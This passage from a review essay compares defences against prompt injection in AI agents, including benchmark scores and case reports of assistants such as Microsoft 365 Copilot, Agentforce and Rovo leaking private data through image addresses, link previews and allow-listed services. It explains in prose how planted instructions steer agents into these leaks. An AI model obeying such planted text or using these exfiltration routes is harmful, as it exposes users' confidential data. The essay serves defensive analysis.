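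Other researchers have since tested Progent, with different results. *Bounded Agents* (2026) ran it on Claude Sonnet 4.6 with hand-written rules and observed no successful attacks. Under attack, the agent completed 88.5% of the office tasks and 59.7% of the banking tasks. But when Li and colleagues ran Progent on the PASB benchmark, attack success against gpt-5.6-luna fell only from 97.5% to 62.5%. Progent enforces whatever rules it has, so this poor result may mean that the rules did not suit the new environment.

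Li and colleagues' own design, PACE (October 2026), runs two checks just before each action. One traces whether untrusted or secret data could have influenced the action, and the other determines whether the user's request authorises the action's effects. They tested PACE on eight benchmarks with gpt-5.6-luna, Qwen-3.8-27B and DeepSeek-V4-Flash. On AgentDojo, it reduced attack success from 48–100% without a defence to 0–8%. Utility fell by less than three points on AgentDojo and by at most three on AgentDyn, where CaMeL had failed almost completely.

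These are the best results of any design here, but a smaller experiment by the same team gives some reason for caution. The team used Qwen to test PACE with various parts switched off on 1,167 selected cases. On these cases, the full system cut AgentDyn utility from 67% to 33%. This doesn't necessarily contradict the main test, because the selection has a different mix of tasks from the full benchmark, but the small loss of utility in the main test evidently depends on the mix.

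In the same experiment, either check alone stopped every selected AgentDojo attack, but tracing influence alone cut AgentDojo utility from 77% to 14%, while checking authorisation alone left it at 65%. A rule against any action that untrusted text might have influenced blocks a lot of legitimate work, because agents mostly read things in order to act on them. The tested version of PACE therefore allows some actions that fail the tracing check but pass the authorisation check. This preserves utility, but the team's formal proof about blocked data paths does not cover everything the tested version does.

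### Stopping leaks at the network

The designs above mostly protect tools such as email and payments. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) examines web requests, which can carry private data in their addresses. The researchers tested an agent running on qwen2.5:7b, a small open-weight model. They put a secret in its context and asked it to summarise a web page that contained planted instructions.

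The agent leaked data in 423 of 480 undefended runs, or 88%. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user looked harmless, so a filter on the answer would have missed the leak. None of the 120 runs with ordinary pages sent anything to the attacker. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that the set-up favoured the attacker, because the secret was directly visible to the model and the system had few instructions about security.

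A separate experiment tested each defence in 30 runs against a single type of attack. All 30 undefended runs leaked. Telling the model to ignore instructions from web pages reduced this to 20, while marking the page's text as untrusted made no difference alone. With both measures, 17 runs still leaked.

The model tried to send the secret in all 30 runs, but software enforcing an allow-list of four domains blocked every request. A defence called "redirect detection" also stopped every leak. It is actually a block-list of suspicious-looking addresses, so it would be weaker against an attacker with an ordinary-looking address.

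This is good evidence that instructing a small model to behave safely is less reliable than blocking its requests. It is much weaker evidence that allow-lists work better than filters, because two filters on outgoing requests also brought leaks to zero. One filter searched for words such as "password" and the other for random-looking strings.

The results for those filters are a little odd, however. Neither filter acts until the model has composed a request, yet the model tried to leak in only 23% of runs with the keyword filter and in none with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking strings when it is being monitored, but that seems to require the model to know about the monitoring.

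The allow-list's perfect score also follows from the set-up, since Lan and colleagues deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was not on the list. They note that real attackers might go through a listed site that has been compromised or that redirects elsewhere. Their comparison has no utility score, and an agent that could contact only four domains would be useless for most web research.

### The scores side by side

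The table gives one or two results for each design. For FIDES, it shows the number of successful attacks instead of a rate.

| Restriction | Tested by | Model and test | Attack success, without → with | Utility with no attack, without → with |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tool filter | Debenedetti and colleagues | GPT-4o, AgentDojo | about half → 7.5% | 69% without it |
| Tool filter | Li and colleagues | gpt-5.6-luna, MSB | 98.8% → 52.5% | 89.1% → 91.0% |
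| CaMeL | Li and colleagues | gpt-5.6-luna, AgentDojo | 100% → 36.1% | 73.8% → 57.0% |
| CaMeL | Li and colleagues | gpt-5.6-luna, AgentDyn | 19.5% → 0% | 74.8% → 0% |
| FIDES | Costa and colleagues | GPT-4o, AgentDojo | 152 attacks → 0 | 84% → 50% |
| Progent | Shi and colleagues | GPT-4o, AgentDojo | 39.9% → 1.0% | about the same |
| PACE | Li and colleagues | gpt-5.6-luna, AgentDojo | 100% → 8.1% | 73.8% → 72.1% |
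| PACE | Li and colleagues | gpt-5.6-luna, AgentDyn | 19.5% → 0% | 74.8% → 73.6% |
| Allow-list of domains | Lan and colleagues | qwen2.5:7b, 30 runs | 100% → 0% | no score |
| Strict allow-list | *aiAuthZ* | two 2026 models, 20 AgentDojo cases | 0% → 0% | 100% → 80% |

These numbers are a poor basis for ranking the designs, partly because the tests used different attacks. The standard AgentDojo attack never worked on the two undefended models in *aiAuthZ*, whereas the strongest group of attacks in Li and colleagues' test worked every time on an undefended gpt-5.6-luna.

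The cases also differ between papers that use the same benchmark. Shi and colleagues dropped two AgentDojo attacks that try to make the agent prefer a different hotel. *Bounded Agents* measured utility on 949 AgentDojo pairs, but measured security only on the 609 whose attacks involve calling a tool. In *aiAuthZ*, a single blocked payment to a new payee caused the 20-point fall in utility, so the utility score must be based on very few distinct tasks.

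Even the definition of a successful attack varies. AgentDojo's code can count an attack as successful when the software blocked the forbidden action the agent tried. Shi and colleagues corrected such errors by hand for one attack. Costa and colleagues also checked their results by hand and lowered the number of successful attacks against FIDES from 3 to 0.

Finally, results can depend on who runs the test. Most of the newer figures for CaMeL come from the creators of a rival design, who had less reason to make CaMeL perform well. In the same tests, FIDES did worse than no defence on WASP, a benchmark of web tasks. With Qwen, attack success rose from 19% to 40%, and the agent completed no tasks. FIDES is very unlikely to have given the agent new abilities, so the result probably reflects a poor fit between FIDES and that benchmark more than a weakness in labelling data.

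Comparisons within one experiment are more trustworthy, and they show fairly consistently that restrictions based on the details of an action tend to preserve more utility than those that remove a whole tool or fix the whole plan. These finer restrictions also require someone to write more detailed rules and get them right.

### What the benchmarks leave out

Most of these tests use attacks written in advance, and Nasr and colleagues' results show how misleading this can be. An adaptive attacker should weaken a restriction less than a filter, because rewording an attack cannot restore a missing tool. The attacker could still look for another tool with the same effect or try to influence the rules.

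The evidence that tool restrictions withstand adaptive attacks is encouraging but thin. Shi and colleagues tried three adaptive attacks on Progent, some aimed at the model that updates its rules, and attack success rose only slightly. Li and colleagues ran an automated search for attacks on 30 AgentDojo cases, with up to 50 attempts at each. It succeeded in 21 cases without a defence and in none with PACE. With so few cases, the true success rate against PACE could be as high as about 11%. In tests by Kurakin and colleagues, attackers were still finding new successes after 150 attempts, so a limit of 50 may be too low.

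*AutoDojo* (2026), which generates new attacks automatically, found that attack success also depends on how the user words the request. On banking tasks with an undefended Gemini-2.5-Flash, attacks succeeded in 67% of cases when the user left the choice of action open and in 14% when the user specified everything. A benchmark made up mostly of precise requests will therefore underestimate the risk to users who leave more decisions to the agent.

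Designers of defences also know more about a benchmark's attacks than they would about a real attacker's. Costa and colleagues labelled a type of data as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. Their result of zero successful attacks shows that FIDES works when the labels are right. A company labelling its own data would have to guess where attacks might come from, and might miss a source.

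Utility scores have a similar gap, because they cover only the tasks that the benchmark's creators wrote. AgentDojo's tasks involve only text, so an agent that could no longer display images would score the same, although its users might miss the charts and photographs. Utility scores also omit the requests that people stop making once they learn that the agent will refuse.

The scores also don't measure how much an agent irritates the user. A task counts as complete whether the agent finished it alone or interrupted the user five times. Only 6% of Progent's rule changes required approval, but in the main test software gave that approval, so no one had to read the requests. Other researchers have run experiments on how people respond to such requests.

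Most of these tests also barely measure deception of the user. Shi and colleagues, for example, dropped the hotel attacks, arguing that someone who controls a hotel's listing can simply lie in it without prompt injection. That is true, but the user still gets bad advice. Costa and colleagues likewise did not count attacks that alter text without changing the agent's actions or leaking secrets.

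## Case reports of images that leaked data

AgentDojo's tasks contain no images, so the evidence about image display comes from real products. Since 2023, researchers have repeatedly made assistants leak private data through the addresses of the images they display. Companies often responded by limiting the sites that images could come from, but this failed several times because a permitted site could pass the data on. Anthropic made users click before an image was shown, and Google stopped its Gemini assistant from showing outside images.

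### Bing Chat and the browser's own rule

Chat assistants usually format their answers in Markdown, which represents an image as a short piece of text containing a web address. When the application displays the image, the browser fetches it from that address, so anyone who can influence the answer can influence which sites the browser contacts.

Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes an early case. Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog, found that a comment or an advertisement on a web page could take over Microsoft's Bing Chat and make it leak other data from the page and a summary of the conversation. Rehberger reported this on 8 April 2023. Microsoft announced a fix on 15 June, and the old tests then stopped working.

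At least part of the fix was a Content Security Policy, a rule that a website sends to the browser with a page. The rule can list the sites from which the page may load images. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* explains that the browser will not load images from anywhere else. Bing Chat's list had four addresses, all belonging to Bing, so the assistant could still show pictures it had created for the user.

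A Content Security Policy usually lists whole sites, not exact addresses. If `pictures.example` is on the list, the browser will request any image address there, including one with a stolen password at the end. The password leaks only if an attacker can find out what `pictures.example` receives, so the list is safe only if attackers can't do this for any site on it.

The policy is also public, since every visitor's browser receives a copy. Researchers can inspect it for mistakes, and so can attackers.

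### Other early repairs

Anthropic fixed a similar leak in Claude differently. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Claude no longer loaded images automatically, and users had to click "Show Image" to see one. Rehberger had reported the leak, which started from a hostile file that the user had uploaded, on 12 July 2023, and Anthropic closed the report two weeks later. He thought the fix imperfect but agreed that it stopped the automatic leak, so an attacker would now have to get the user to click.

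OpenAI took much longer, having known about the leak in ChatGPT since April 2023 and at first declined to fix it. In December, ChatGPT's web application began checking with an OpenAI server that an image's address was safe before displaying the image. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* found two gaps in this fix. The iPhone app did not make the check, so the original leak still worked there. In a quick test of 36 addresses on Rehberger's own site, nine passed the check, which was enough to leak small amounts of data slowly.

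OpenAI did not publish its criteria, so nobody outside the company could tell why those nine had passed. Rehberger guessed that the server might look images up in a search index, which would resemble the known-URL rule OpenAI later described for links. Rehberger also suggested showing only a few images per answer, which would limit a leak even when the check made mistakes.

In 2024 GitHub stopped its programming assistant, Copilot Chat, from displaying images hosted on untrusted domains. Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, lists ChatGPT, Google Bard, Writer.com, Amazon Q and Google's NotebookLM as earlier examples of products that could leak data through images.

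Google has since gone further with Gemini. It says, in a statement quoted by the security company Checkmarx, that its software identifies images hosted elsewhere and does not display them. This removes outside images, so an attacker has no list of permitted sites to search.

However, companies do not all agree that every such leak needs fixing. Checkmarx reports that Microsoft did not treat a similar leak in Copilot Chat as a vulnerability and did not commit to fixing it. Google has been inconsistent. In November 2025, a researcher reported an image leak in Antigravity, Google's coding product, and Google classed the behaviour as intended.

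### An expired domain and an online form

Two later cases show how an allow-list can fail although the browser enforces it perfectly. Both appear in Willison's collection *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*.

Salesforce sells Agentforce to companies for running AI agents on their customer records. Strangers can add to those records, because many companies let prospective customers submit their details through a public web form. Salesforce had limited the sites from which Agentforce could load images, but one of the domains on its list had expired. In 2025, Sasi Levi and the security company Noma Security registered that domain and showed that a malicious form entry could make the agent send customers' email addresses to that domain.

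The domain was presumably safe when Salesforce put it on the list, but it became dangerous when its registration lapsed. The browser's rule would not have detected the change of owner. Salesforce corrected the list and then added a second one, "Trusted URLs", to stop the agent from producing links to untrusted domains.

Superhuman, an email application with an AI assistant, allowed images to load from `docs.google.com`. Google still owned that domain, but the domain also hosts Google Forms, which can store data sent in an image request. PromptArmor showed that one hostile email could make the assistant send the contents of dozens of other emails, including financial, legal and medical ones, to an attacker's form. Willison reported the case in January 2026 and praised Superhuman for treating it as urgent and issuing a fix.

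A company can prevent the Agentforce problem by regularly checking who owns each domain on its list. The Superhuman problem is harder to prevent, because someone has to know everything a large site can do with a request, including functions unrelated to images. The site's owner can also add a function without telling the companies that have listed it.

### Three rounds of leaks from Microsoft 365 Copilot

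Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their email, files and chats. It has had three published sets of leaks in 18 months, and each included an image that went out through one of Microsoft's own services.

The first case was EchoLeak. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how an outsider could send an employee an email containing instructions for Copilot. If the employee later asked a question that caused Copilot to retrieve the email, Copilot could follow those instructions and put confidential data into an image address, without the employee clicking anything.

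Microsoft had three defences against this. A classifier meant to catch the hostile email failed. Software was supposed to strip outside links and images from Copilot's answers, but it did not recognise every way of writing them. The Content Security Policy stopped the browser from contacting the attacker's site directly, but it permitted a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch an outside address on request. The browser contacted that service, which forwarded the data to the attacker's site.

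The list Ravia published had 29 different entries, 11 of which covered every address under a domain. If each entry independently had a 2% chance of containing such a weakness, a list of four, like Bing Chat's in 2023, would have about an 8% chance of including at least one, and a list of 29 would have about a 44% chance. The 2% is only an illustration, but a longer list gives attackers more to search, especially when single entries cover many services.

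Aim Labs, Ravia's research group, reported EchoLeak in January 2025, and Microsoft had rolled out the fix by June (Willison, 2025). Microsoft's public description of the flaw is a single sentence, which INCIBE, Spain's cybersecurity institute, reproduces in *CVE-2025-32711* (2025). It attributes the leak to "AI command injection" and does not mention images, Teams or the allow-list. Microsoft also said that it had fully mitigated the problem and that customers did not need to do anything, according to TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit*.

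The description confirms the flaw but does not specify how Microsoft fixed it. The company could have taken the Teams service off the list, stopped that service from fetching outside addresses, or improved the software that strips images. Either of the first two changes would have closed this route permanently, but the third would have left it open to anyone who found another way of writing an image.

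A month after EchoLeak became public, Microsoft said its defences included "deterministic blocking of known data exfiltration methods". Cyber Security News adds that the blocking covers images and malicious links.

Varonis, another security company, describes the next leak, SearchLeak, in a text that the Cloud Security Alliance republished. An employee who clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address would start a search in Copilot. Copilot's answer could then contain an image whose address held the search results. Microsoft had software to clean the answer, but the browser requested the image before the software had finished. The request went to Bing's image service, which was on the allow-list and fetched an outside address. Bing was on the list that Ravia had published about a year earlier.

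Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (4 June 2026) again describes the flaw in one sentence, this time as "command injection". The sentence doesn't mention Bing or the order in which the browser and the cleaning software acted, so readers again can't tell from it which part Microsoft repaired.

The third set suggests that Microsoft did not close the Bing route completely. In *ReLeak*, Simonovich (2026) announced three more leaks that needed no click from the user. One of them again sent data out through an image that Bing fetched, according to Faisal's *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (2026). Ravia's group, now called Cato AI Labs, reported the leaks between 29 July and 20 August, less than three months after the SearchLeak notice. Microsoft closed the image route on 15 November.

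The other two ReLeak routes did not involve displaying an image in an answer:

- Copilot could save a document with confidential data in a link, which Microsoft's own software later opened. Microsoft closed this route on 11 November.
- Copilot could run code in an environment that was supposed to have no network access but did. Microsoft closed this route on 17 September.

If Microsoft had removed all outside images from Copilot, it would probably have prevented EchoLeak's automatic version, SearchLeak and one of the three ReLeak routes. The other two ReLeak routes would still have worked, because they depended on capabilities that Microsoft had added for unrelated reasons. Each needed its own restriction.

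### Link previews and messages to oneself

Stopping an assistant from displaying images may not prevent the same leak if its answers appear in another company's application. Slack and Discord, for example, fetch a title and a preview picture for links posted in a chat. Willison (2024) points out in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* that if an agent posts a link containing private data, fetching the preview can leak the data before anyone clicks.

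PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that link previews could leak data from OpenClaw, a popular agent that people can talk to through chat apps. OpenClaw was exposed by default on Telegram, but changing one setting turns off link previews for its Telegram messages. Developers can also turn off previews for messages their applications post to Slack. In both cases, users seem to lose little, since they keep the link and only the title and thumbnail disappear.

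The leak is hard to prevent because the agent's developer controls what the agent writes, while the chat company controls what happens to a link after it arrives. PromptArmor therefore wants chat companies to let developers turn previews off for a single chat or channel, and agent developers to use the settings that already exist. Until they do, a user who connects an agent to a new chat app may restore a capability that the agent's developer thought was gone.

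Microsoft Copilot Cowork, an agent for office work, had a similar leak inside a single company's products. It could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval. The inbox displayed images from outside sites, so opening a message could send data to an attacker even though the user was the only recipient. The data could include links that let anyone who had them download the user's files from OneDrive, Microsoft's online storage. Willison, who described the case in May 2026, does not mention a fix.

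Microsoft could have closed this leak by requiring users to approve the messages or by not loading outside images in them. The second option seems like the better design to me, since a user asked to approve a message to themselves has little reason to look for a hidden leak.

Atlassian's Rovo is an agent that works with a company's task lists and documents. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* identified two ways data could leak. Rovo displayed outside images, and its tool for opening search results would also open addresses the agent had composed itself. PromptArmor's demonstration mainly used the tool. An administrator who switched off web search would reasonably have believed that Rovo could no longer contact the web, but the tool remained available.

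PromptArmor told Atlassian about both routes on 23 May 2026. More than two months later, Atlassian had given the report a case number and thanked PromptArmor, but Rovo was still vulnerable. PromptArmor then published its findings. Blocking images would not have stopped the main attack, which used the link-opening tool, and data could still have leaked through images if Atlassian had blocked only that tool.

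### Demonstrations and actual harm

Nearly everything known about these leaks comes from people who leaked their own test data. A successful leak is good evidence that a route existed. If the same test fails after the company makes a change, as happened with Bing Chat, that is good evidence that the company closed the route. These tests give almost no information about how often attackers used the route before then.

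The companies and the people who found these flaws mostly report no victims. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak affected no customers. ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* describes SearchLeak as a research demonstration and reports no known active exploitation. Cato knows of no attacks that used ReLeak.

OECD's *Critical SearchLeak Vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot Exposes Sensitive Data* (2026), an AI-generated entry in an incident database, describes SearchLeak as "directly causing harm through unauthorized data exfiltration", but the incident seems to have been a demonstration rather than an attack. Counting incidents in such a database will therefore probably overestimate how many people these leaks have harmed.

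There may be victims nobody knows about, because these leaks are hard to notice. A Rovo user who came back to the chat would see ordinary suggestions about their tasks and no trace of the theft. Microsoft was better placed to look for victims of EchoLeak and SearchLeak because the data passed through its own servers, but it has not explained how it checked.

Severity ratings estimate how bad an attack could be, not how many attacks have happened. The Next Web reports that Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical on its own scale. On a common industry scale, Microsoft gave it 6.5 out of 10, or medium, partly because the user had to click. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5 after assessing it as needing no action from the user.

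Many of the finders also sell security products or services, which gives them a reason to make a leak sound alarming. Ravia's post advertises Aim Labs' own guardrails as protection against EchoLeak. It also claims "the complete compromise of M365 Copilot data integrity". "Integrity" is an odd word here, because a loss of integrity in security means that someone has altered data, and EchoLeak copied it.

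I would still trust the demonstrations, because Microsoft, Salesforce and Superhuman all fixed the flaws that outsiders reported and would have had little reason to do so if the leaks weren't real. The finders' commercial interest matters more when they recommend a remedy. Aim Labs proposes a filter that detects when an outsider's email refers to private data, but its own report shows that closing the forwarding service would have blocked that route whatever the email contained.

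These reports are also subject to a selection effect, because researchers publish the leaks they find but seldom publish failed attempts. A product without any reports may be well designed, or it may never have been tested. We therefore cannot calculate a failure rate for allow-lists from the number of reported failures.

### The repairs side by side

The table includes Gemini's restriction for comparison, although it was not a response to any one leak described here.

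| Product | Date | Capability left open | Repair | Kind of repair |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | June 2023 | Images from any site | Content Security Policy with a few Bing addresses | Allow-list |
| Claude | July 2023 | Images from any site | User clicks "Show Image" | Click |
| ChatGPT | December 2023 | Images from any site | Server checks each address; web application only at first | Automatic check |
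| GitHub Copilot Chat | 2024 | Images from untrusted domains | Those images blocked | Allow-list |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (EchoLeak) | June 2025 | Images through a listed Teams service | Microsoft's fix, mechanism not stated | Unknown |
| Gemini | 2025 or later | None for outside images | Outside images not displayed | Removal |
| Salesforce Agentforce | September 2025 | Images from an expired domain on the list | List corrected, "Trusted URLs" added | Allow-list |
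| Superhuman | January 2026 | Images from a listed domain that also stored form data | Fix issued, mechanism not stated | Unknown |
| OpenClaw on Telegram | 2026 | Link previews | Setting that turns previews off | Removal, if the user chooses it |
| Copilot Cowork | May 2026 | Outside images in messages to the user | None reported | None |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (SearchLeak) | June 2026 | Images through Bing | Microsoft's fix, mechanism not stated | Unknown |
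| Atlassian Rovo | Reported May 2026 | Opening composed addresses; outside images | None when PromptArmor published | None |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (ReLeak, image route) | November 2026 | Images through Bing | Microsoft's fix, mechanism not stated | Unknown |

In EchoLeak, Agentforce, Superhuman and SearchLeak, the data left through a site on an allow-list, and the same was probably true of ReLeak's image route. The lists were still useful, because without them an attacker could have used any site on the web and would not have needed to find an expired domain or a forwarding service. But a list gets weaker over time if nobody reviews it, and it is harder to review when the sites on it are large.

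Removing outside images avoids that work, but it depends on software recognising every image, and EchoLeak got past software meant to do this. A company can also send the browser a Content Security Policy that permits no outside sites, so that any image the software misses still does not load.

Users would then lose photographs from news sites, product pictures in shopping answers, and charts hosted elsewhere, but they could keep the pictures that the assistant makes. Bing Chat's fix kept those by allowing images from only a few addresses, although the later leaks through Bing show that even a company's own domain can be risky. The safest exception would be a server that only stores the assistant's pictures, cannot fetch outside addresses, and keeps no records that an outsider could read.

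## Rules on which links an agent may open

An assistant can do most of its work without displaying outside images, but it is of little use for research if it cannot open web pages. OpenAI, Anthropic and Google have therefore kept web access and limited which addresses their agents may open. An address can only contain a secret if someone has put it there, so it is fairly safe for an agent to open an address that it did not write itself. OpenAI checks this by looking for the address in a record of public pages, while Anthropic checks how the address entered the conversation.

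### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI described its rule in January 2026 and published a longer technical paper alongside it. The rule works like this:

1. A crawler, a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the addresses of public pages. It has no access to anyone's conversations or accounts.
2. When ChatGPT is about to open an address automatically, software looks for that exact address in the record.
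3. If the address is there, ChatGPT can load the page or image without asking.
4. If it isn't, the software treats the address as unverified. It either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning and waits.

The match has to be exact because even a small addition to an address can leak private information. Suppose the crawler has recorded `news.example/budget`. If a hostile page gets the agent to add the user's salary to the end of that address, the new address will not match, even if the site is reputable.

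The warning, titled "Check this link is safe", tells the user that the link may share information from the conversation, shows the address, and lets the user copy or open it.

A list of trusted websites would be simpler, but OpenAI found two problems with it. First, a trusted site may redirect the agent to an attacker's site. Exact matching largely solves this, because a redirect from a fixed public address has no private data to pass on. Second, people visit many sites besides the popular ones, so a strict list would produce frequent false alarms, which OpenAI thinks can train people to click through warnings without thinking. An index can be much longer because nobody has to decide whether each site deserves trust. It will still miss some pages, and OpenAI's post gives no figure for how often users see the warning.

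The rule is meant only to stop the agent from quietly leaking the user's data through a web address. It does not make the page trustworthy, and a phishing page could pass the check once the crawler had recorded it.

### Anthropic's rule about where an address came from

Anthropic's web fetch tool restricts links by where Claude got them and does not depend on a public index. Developers can add the tool to their products, and the Claude app has a version of it. According to the tool's documentation, "Claude is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs." A newer, Chinese-language edition, *網頁擷取工具*, lists the allowed sources of addresses: the user's messages, earlier searches and fetches, and tools that the developer runs. The tool rejects an address that appears only in Claude's own output.

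When Anthropic released the tool in September 2025, Willison thought its ban on addresses composed by the model gave more protection than its other rules on where an address may come from. He was less happy with how it treated user messages. Many applications paste emails or web pages into the message they send to the model, so an address written by a stranger can count as the user's own.

Results from a developer's tools have a similar weakness. Some tools repeat text that Claude gave them, for instance in an error message, and an address in that text becomes permitted by default. Developers can now exclude particular tools or turn off a whole source, but they have to know the problem exists.

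According to the newer documentation, the tool also refuses to open an address that seems to contain a password or similar credential, unless the credential appeared in the user's message or the developer's instructions. This check would do little to protect a medical diagnosis or the name of the user's employer, because neither looks like a credential.

### Two requests under both rules

Suppose a user pastes the address of a planning notice that a town council published this morning and asks for a summary. Claude can open the page because the user supplied the address. OpenAI's crawler has probably not recorded the address yet, so it would count as unverified under OpenAI's published rule. ChatGPT probably opens the page anyway. Johann Rehberger writes in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that, as far as he knows, ChatGPT treats an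 address in a user's message as safe for the rest of the session.

The results differ more if the user supplies only the council's home page and the agent has to find the notice from there. The link to the notice would not be in the index, so ChatGPT would have to look elsewhere or show the warning. The Claude app would not follow the link, because Anthropic blocks it from opening links it finds on fetched pages. A developer's product using the web fetch tool would follow the link by default. ChatGPT could follow links to last year's notices without asking, because a crawler has had time to record them. The Claude app could open those notices only if a search returned them.

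Now suppose the user wants a second-hand bicycle near Leeds for under £300. Many shopping sites put search terms in the address, so the obvious next step is to open something like this:

`https://bikes.example/search?place=leeds&max=300`

Claude may not open that address, because Claude wrote it. ChatGPT can open it automatically only if the crawler has recorded the same search. Otherwise, the user may see a warning that the link could contain information from the conversation. The link does contain such information, but the user wants the shop to have it. Neither rule distinguishes this request from a leak, because in both cases the model has put information from the conversation into an address.

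Claude could instead run an ordinary web search and open the results, though these might not include bicycles listed that day. The user could also paste the composed address back into the chat, which would allow Claude to open it. This works as a kind of approval, but it is a clumsy way to search.

### Chrome's limits on where an agent can type

An agent that controls a browser can search a shop's site without writing the search address itself. It can type "Leeds" into the search box, and the site's form will build the address. A rule that checks only the addresses the model writes would miss this search, even though it also sends data to the site.

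In *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, Parker (2025) describes a deterministic check for the agent in Google's Chrome browser that restricts addresses written by the model to "known, public URLs". This sounds much like OpenAI's rule, though Parker does not explain how Google decides that an address is known.

The design also limits the agent to sites relevant to the task. Chrome sorts these into sites the agent can only read and sites where it can also click and type. For example, if the user wants the ingredients for a recipe, the agent might read the recipe site and fill a basket at a grocer's site. A hostile comment under the recipe might then make the agent add an unwanted item to the basket, but the agent could not type the user's data into an unrelated site.

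The protection is less certain than the check on addresses, because a model helps judge which sites are relevant. Google doesn't show this model web content, so that a hostile page cannot influence it directly, but the model could still misjudge a site. Google also started with a simpler version that tracked only the sites where the agent could type. Parker explains that the company expected to adjust the system to reduce unnecessary friction, because it had had little chance to see how well the limits suited users' tasks.

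### What the choice of an address can reveal

An agent can leak information about a user through its choice of which page to open, even if it never writes that information into an address. If it opens one page when the user is married and another when the user is single, anyone who can see which page it opened learns whether the user is married. One choice among *N* addresses reveals at most log₂ *N* bits, so a choice between two pages reveals at most one bit, enough to answer one yes-or-no question. Repeated choices can reveal more. A designer can reduce the leak by limiting how many pages the agent opens or by preventing an attacker from supplying the addresses.

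OpenAI has already had to tighten its rules on which links ChatGPT may open. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* describes a demonstration called ZombieAgent, which leaked data through variations in an address that an earlier OpenAI restriction still allowed. OpenAI responded by blocking links from emails unless they appear in a public index or the user has supplied them in the chat. With some preparation, an attacker could still get addresses into an index, and Rehberger reports that OpenAI acknowledges the remaining leak in its own paper.

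Anthropic's rule had a similar gap, which Ayush Paul found and Willison (2026) reported in July. The Claude app's web fetch tool could follow links on pages it had already fetched, so a hostile page could supply the links Claude chose from. In Paul's test, this was enough to reveal the user's name, home city and employer.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already identified the problem internally. It then removed the app's ability to follow links from fetched pages. This is a stronger fix than trying to recognise hostile pages, because it works however convincing a page is. But according to the newer documentation, the developer version still permits such links unless the developer turns them off, so anyone who relies on the default settings keeps a capability that Anthropic considered too risky for its own app.

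Developers can also cap the number of pages that Claude fetches in one turn, although the tool has no cap by default. The tool limits each address to 250 characters, but this does not limit the total amount of data sent across several requests. Lan and colleagues found that splitting a secret across several requests got past simple leak detectors and reduced their measure of leakage in any single request by 73%.

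Rehberger suggests letting the agent request each address only once per session, or having it reuse a stored copy of the page for a few minutes. Either would make it harder to leak data slowly, and most users would lose nothing, since they rarely need a fresh copy of a page they have just read. Pages that change quickly, such as live scores, are an exception.

### A rule that some products do not use

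Rehberger considers OpenAI's rule a significant improvement but not a complete solution. Attacks have become more complicated, and small leaks remain possible. He also worries that some OpenAI developers might not know about the check and might release a feature without it. His worry is reasonable, because OpenAI's earlier check on addresses was missing from ChatGPT's macOS and iOS apps.

Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how Gemini's browsing tool could leak a user's saved information and location. Google had already restricted the links and images in Gemini's answers, but those restrictions did not apply to the browsing tool. Google has since fixed the leak.

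A company could reduce this risk by sending every outgoing request through one piece of software that applies the rule. The rule would then apply even if a team forgot about it. The software would have to cover the tool that opens web pages, image loading, link previews and any code the agent runs.

### Permitted sites that could receive data

Some agents need broader network access than a page-reading tool provides. A coding agent, for example, may have to download software or contact a service that the user's program depends on. Companies often limit such agents to an allow-list of sites, but two of these lists contained sites that attackers could use to collect stolen data.

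Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that can work with a user's files, limited outgoing traffic to a list of domains by default. The list included the domain of Anthropic's developer service, which accepts file uploads from any customer. Willison recounted in January 2026 that PromptArmor had shown a hijacked agent could upload the user's files to an attacker's account on that service.

Of the domains on the list, Anthropic presumably trusted its own most, but that domain serves many customers, and the list did not distinguish the user's account from anyone else's. A known-URL rule alone would not have done so either, because an upload sends the files separately from the address. To stop this leak, the software would have had to restrict what the agent could send and which account could receive it. The web fetch tool avoids this particular problem because it only retrieves pages.

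The default allow-list for the browser tool in Google's Antigravity had a more obvious mistake. It included a public service that records incoming requests for whoever set up the recording. Developers use such services for testing, so its inclusion is understandable, but it gave attackers a ready-made place to receive data. A known-URL rule would probably have blocked this leak, since the agent had to compose an address containing the data. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* reports that Google's approach was to include a disclaimer about the risk, though a disclaimer doesn't remove the service from the list.

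Anthropic also warns in its documentation that two different domain names can look the same to the person checking a list, because a Cyrillic letter can look identical to a Latin one. It suggests using only plain Latin characters where possible. Willison considers an allow-list much stronger protection than the known-URL rule, provided that none of its domains can be used to extract data, but he says finding such domains is "a tricky proposition".

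### Links that appear in an answer

The rules so far mostly limit what the agent opens by itself. Google and Microsoft have also tried removing suspicious links from answers so users cannot click them.

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) explains that Gemini checks links using Safe Browsing, the company's service for identifying dangerous sites. If an email contains an unsafe link, Gemini replaces it in the summary with the words "suspicious link removed". The user can still read the rest of the summary.

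Gemini checks files for suspicious links before using them. If only some of the material is suspicious, according to Google's help page, the user sees a notice that "some content was excluded for security reasons". This protects the user from a bad link, but someone who asked for a summary of ten contracts would still need to find out which one was left out.

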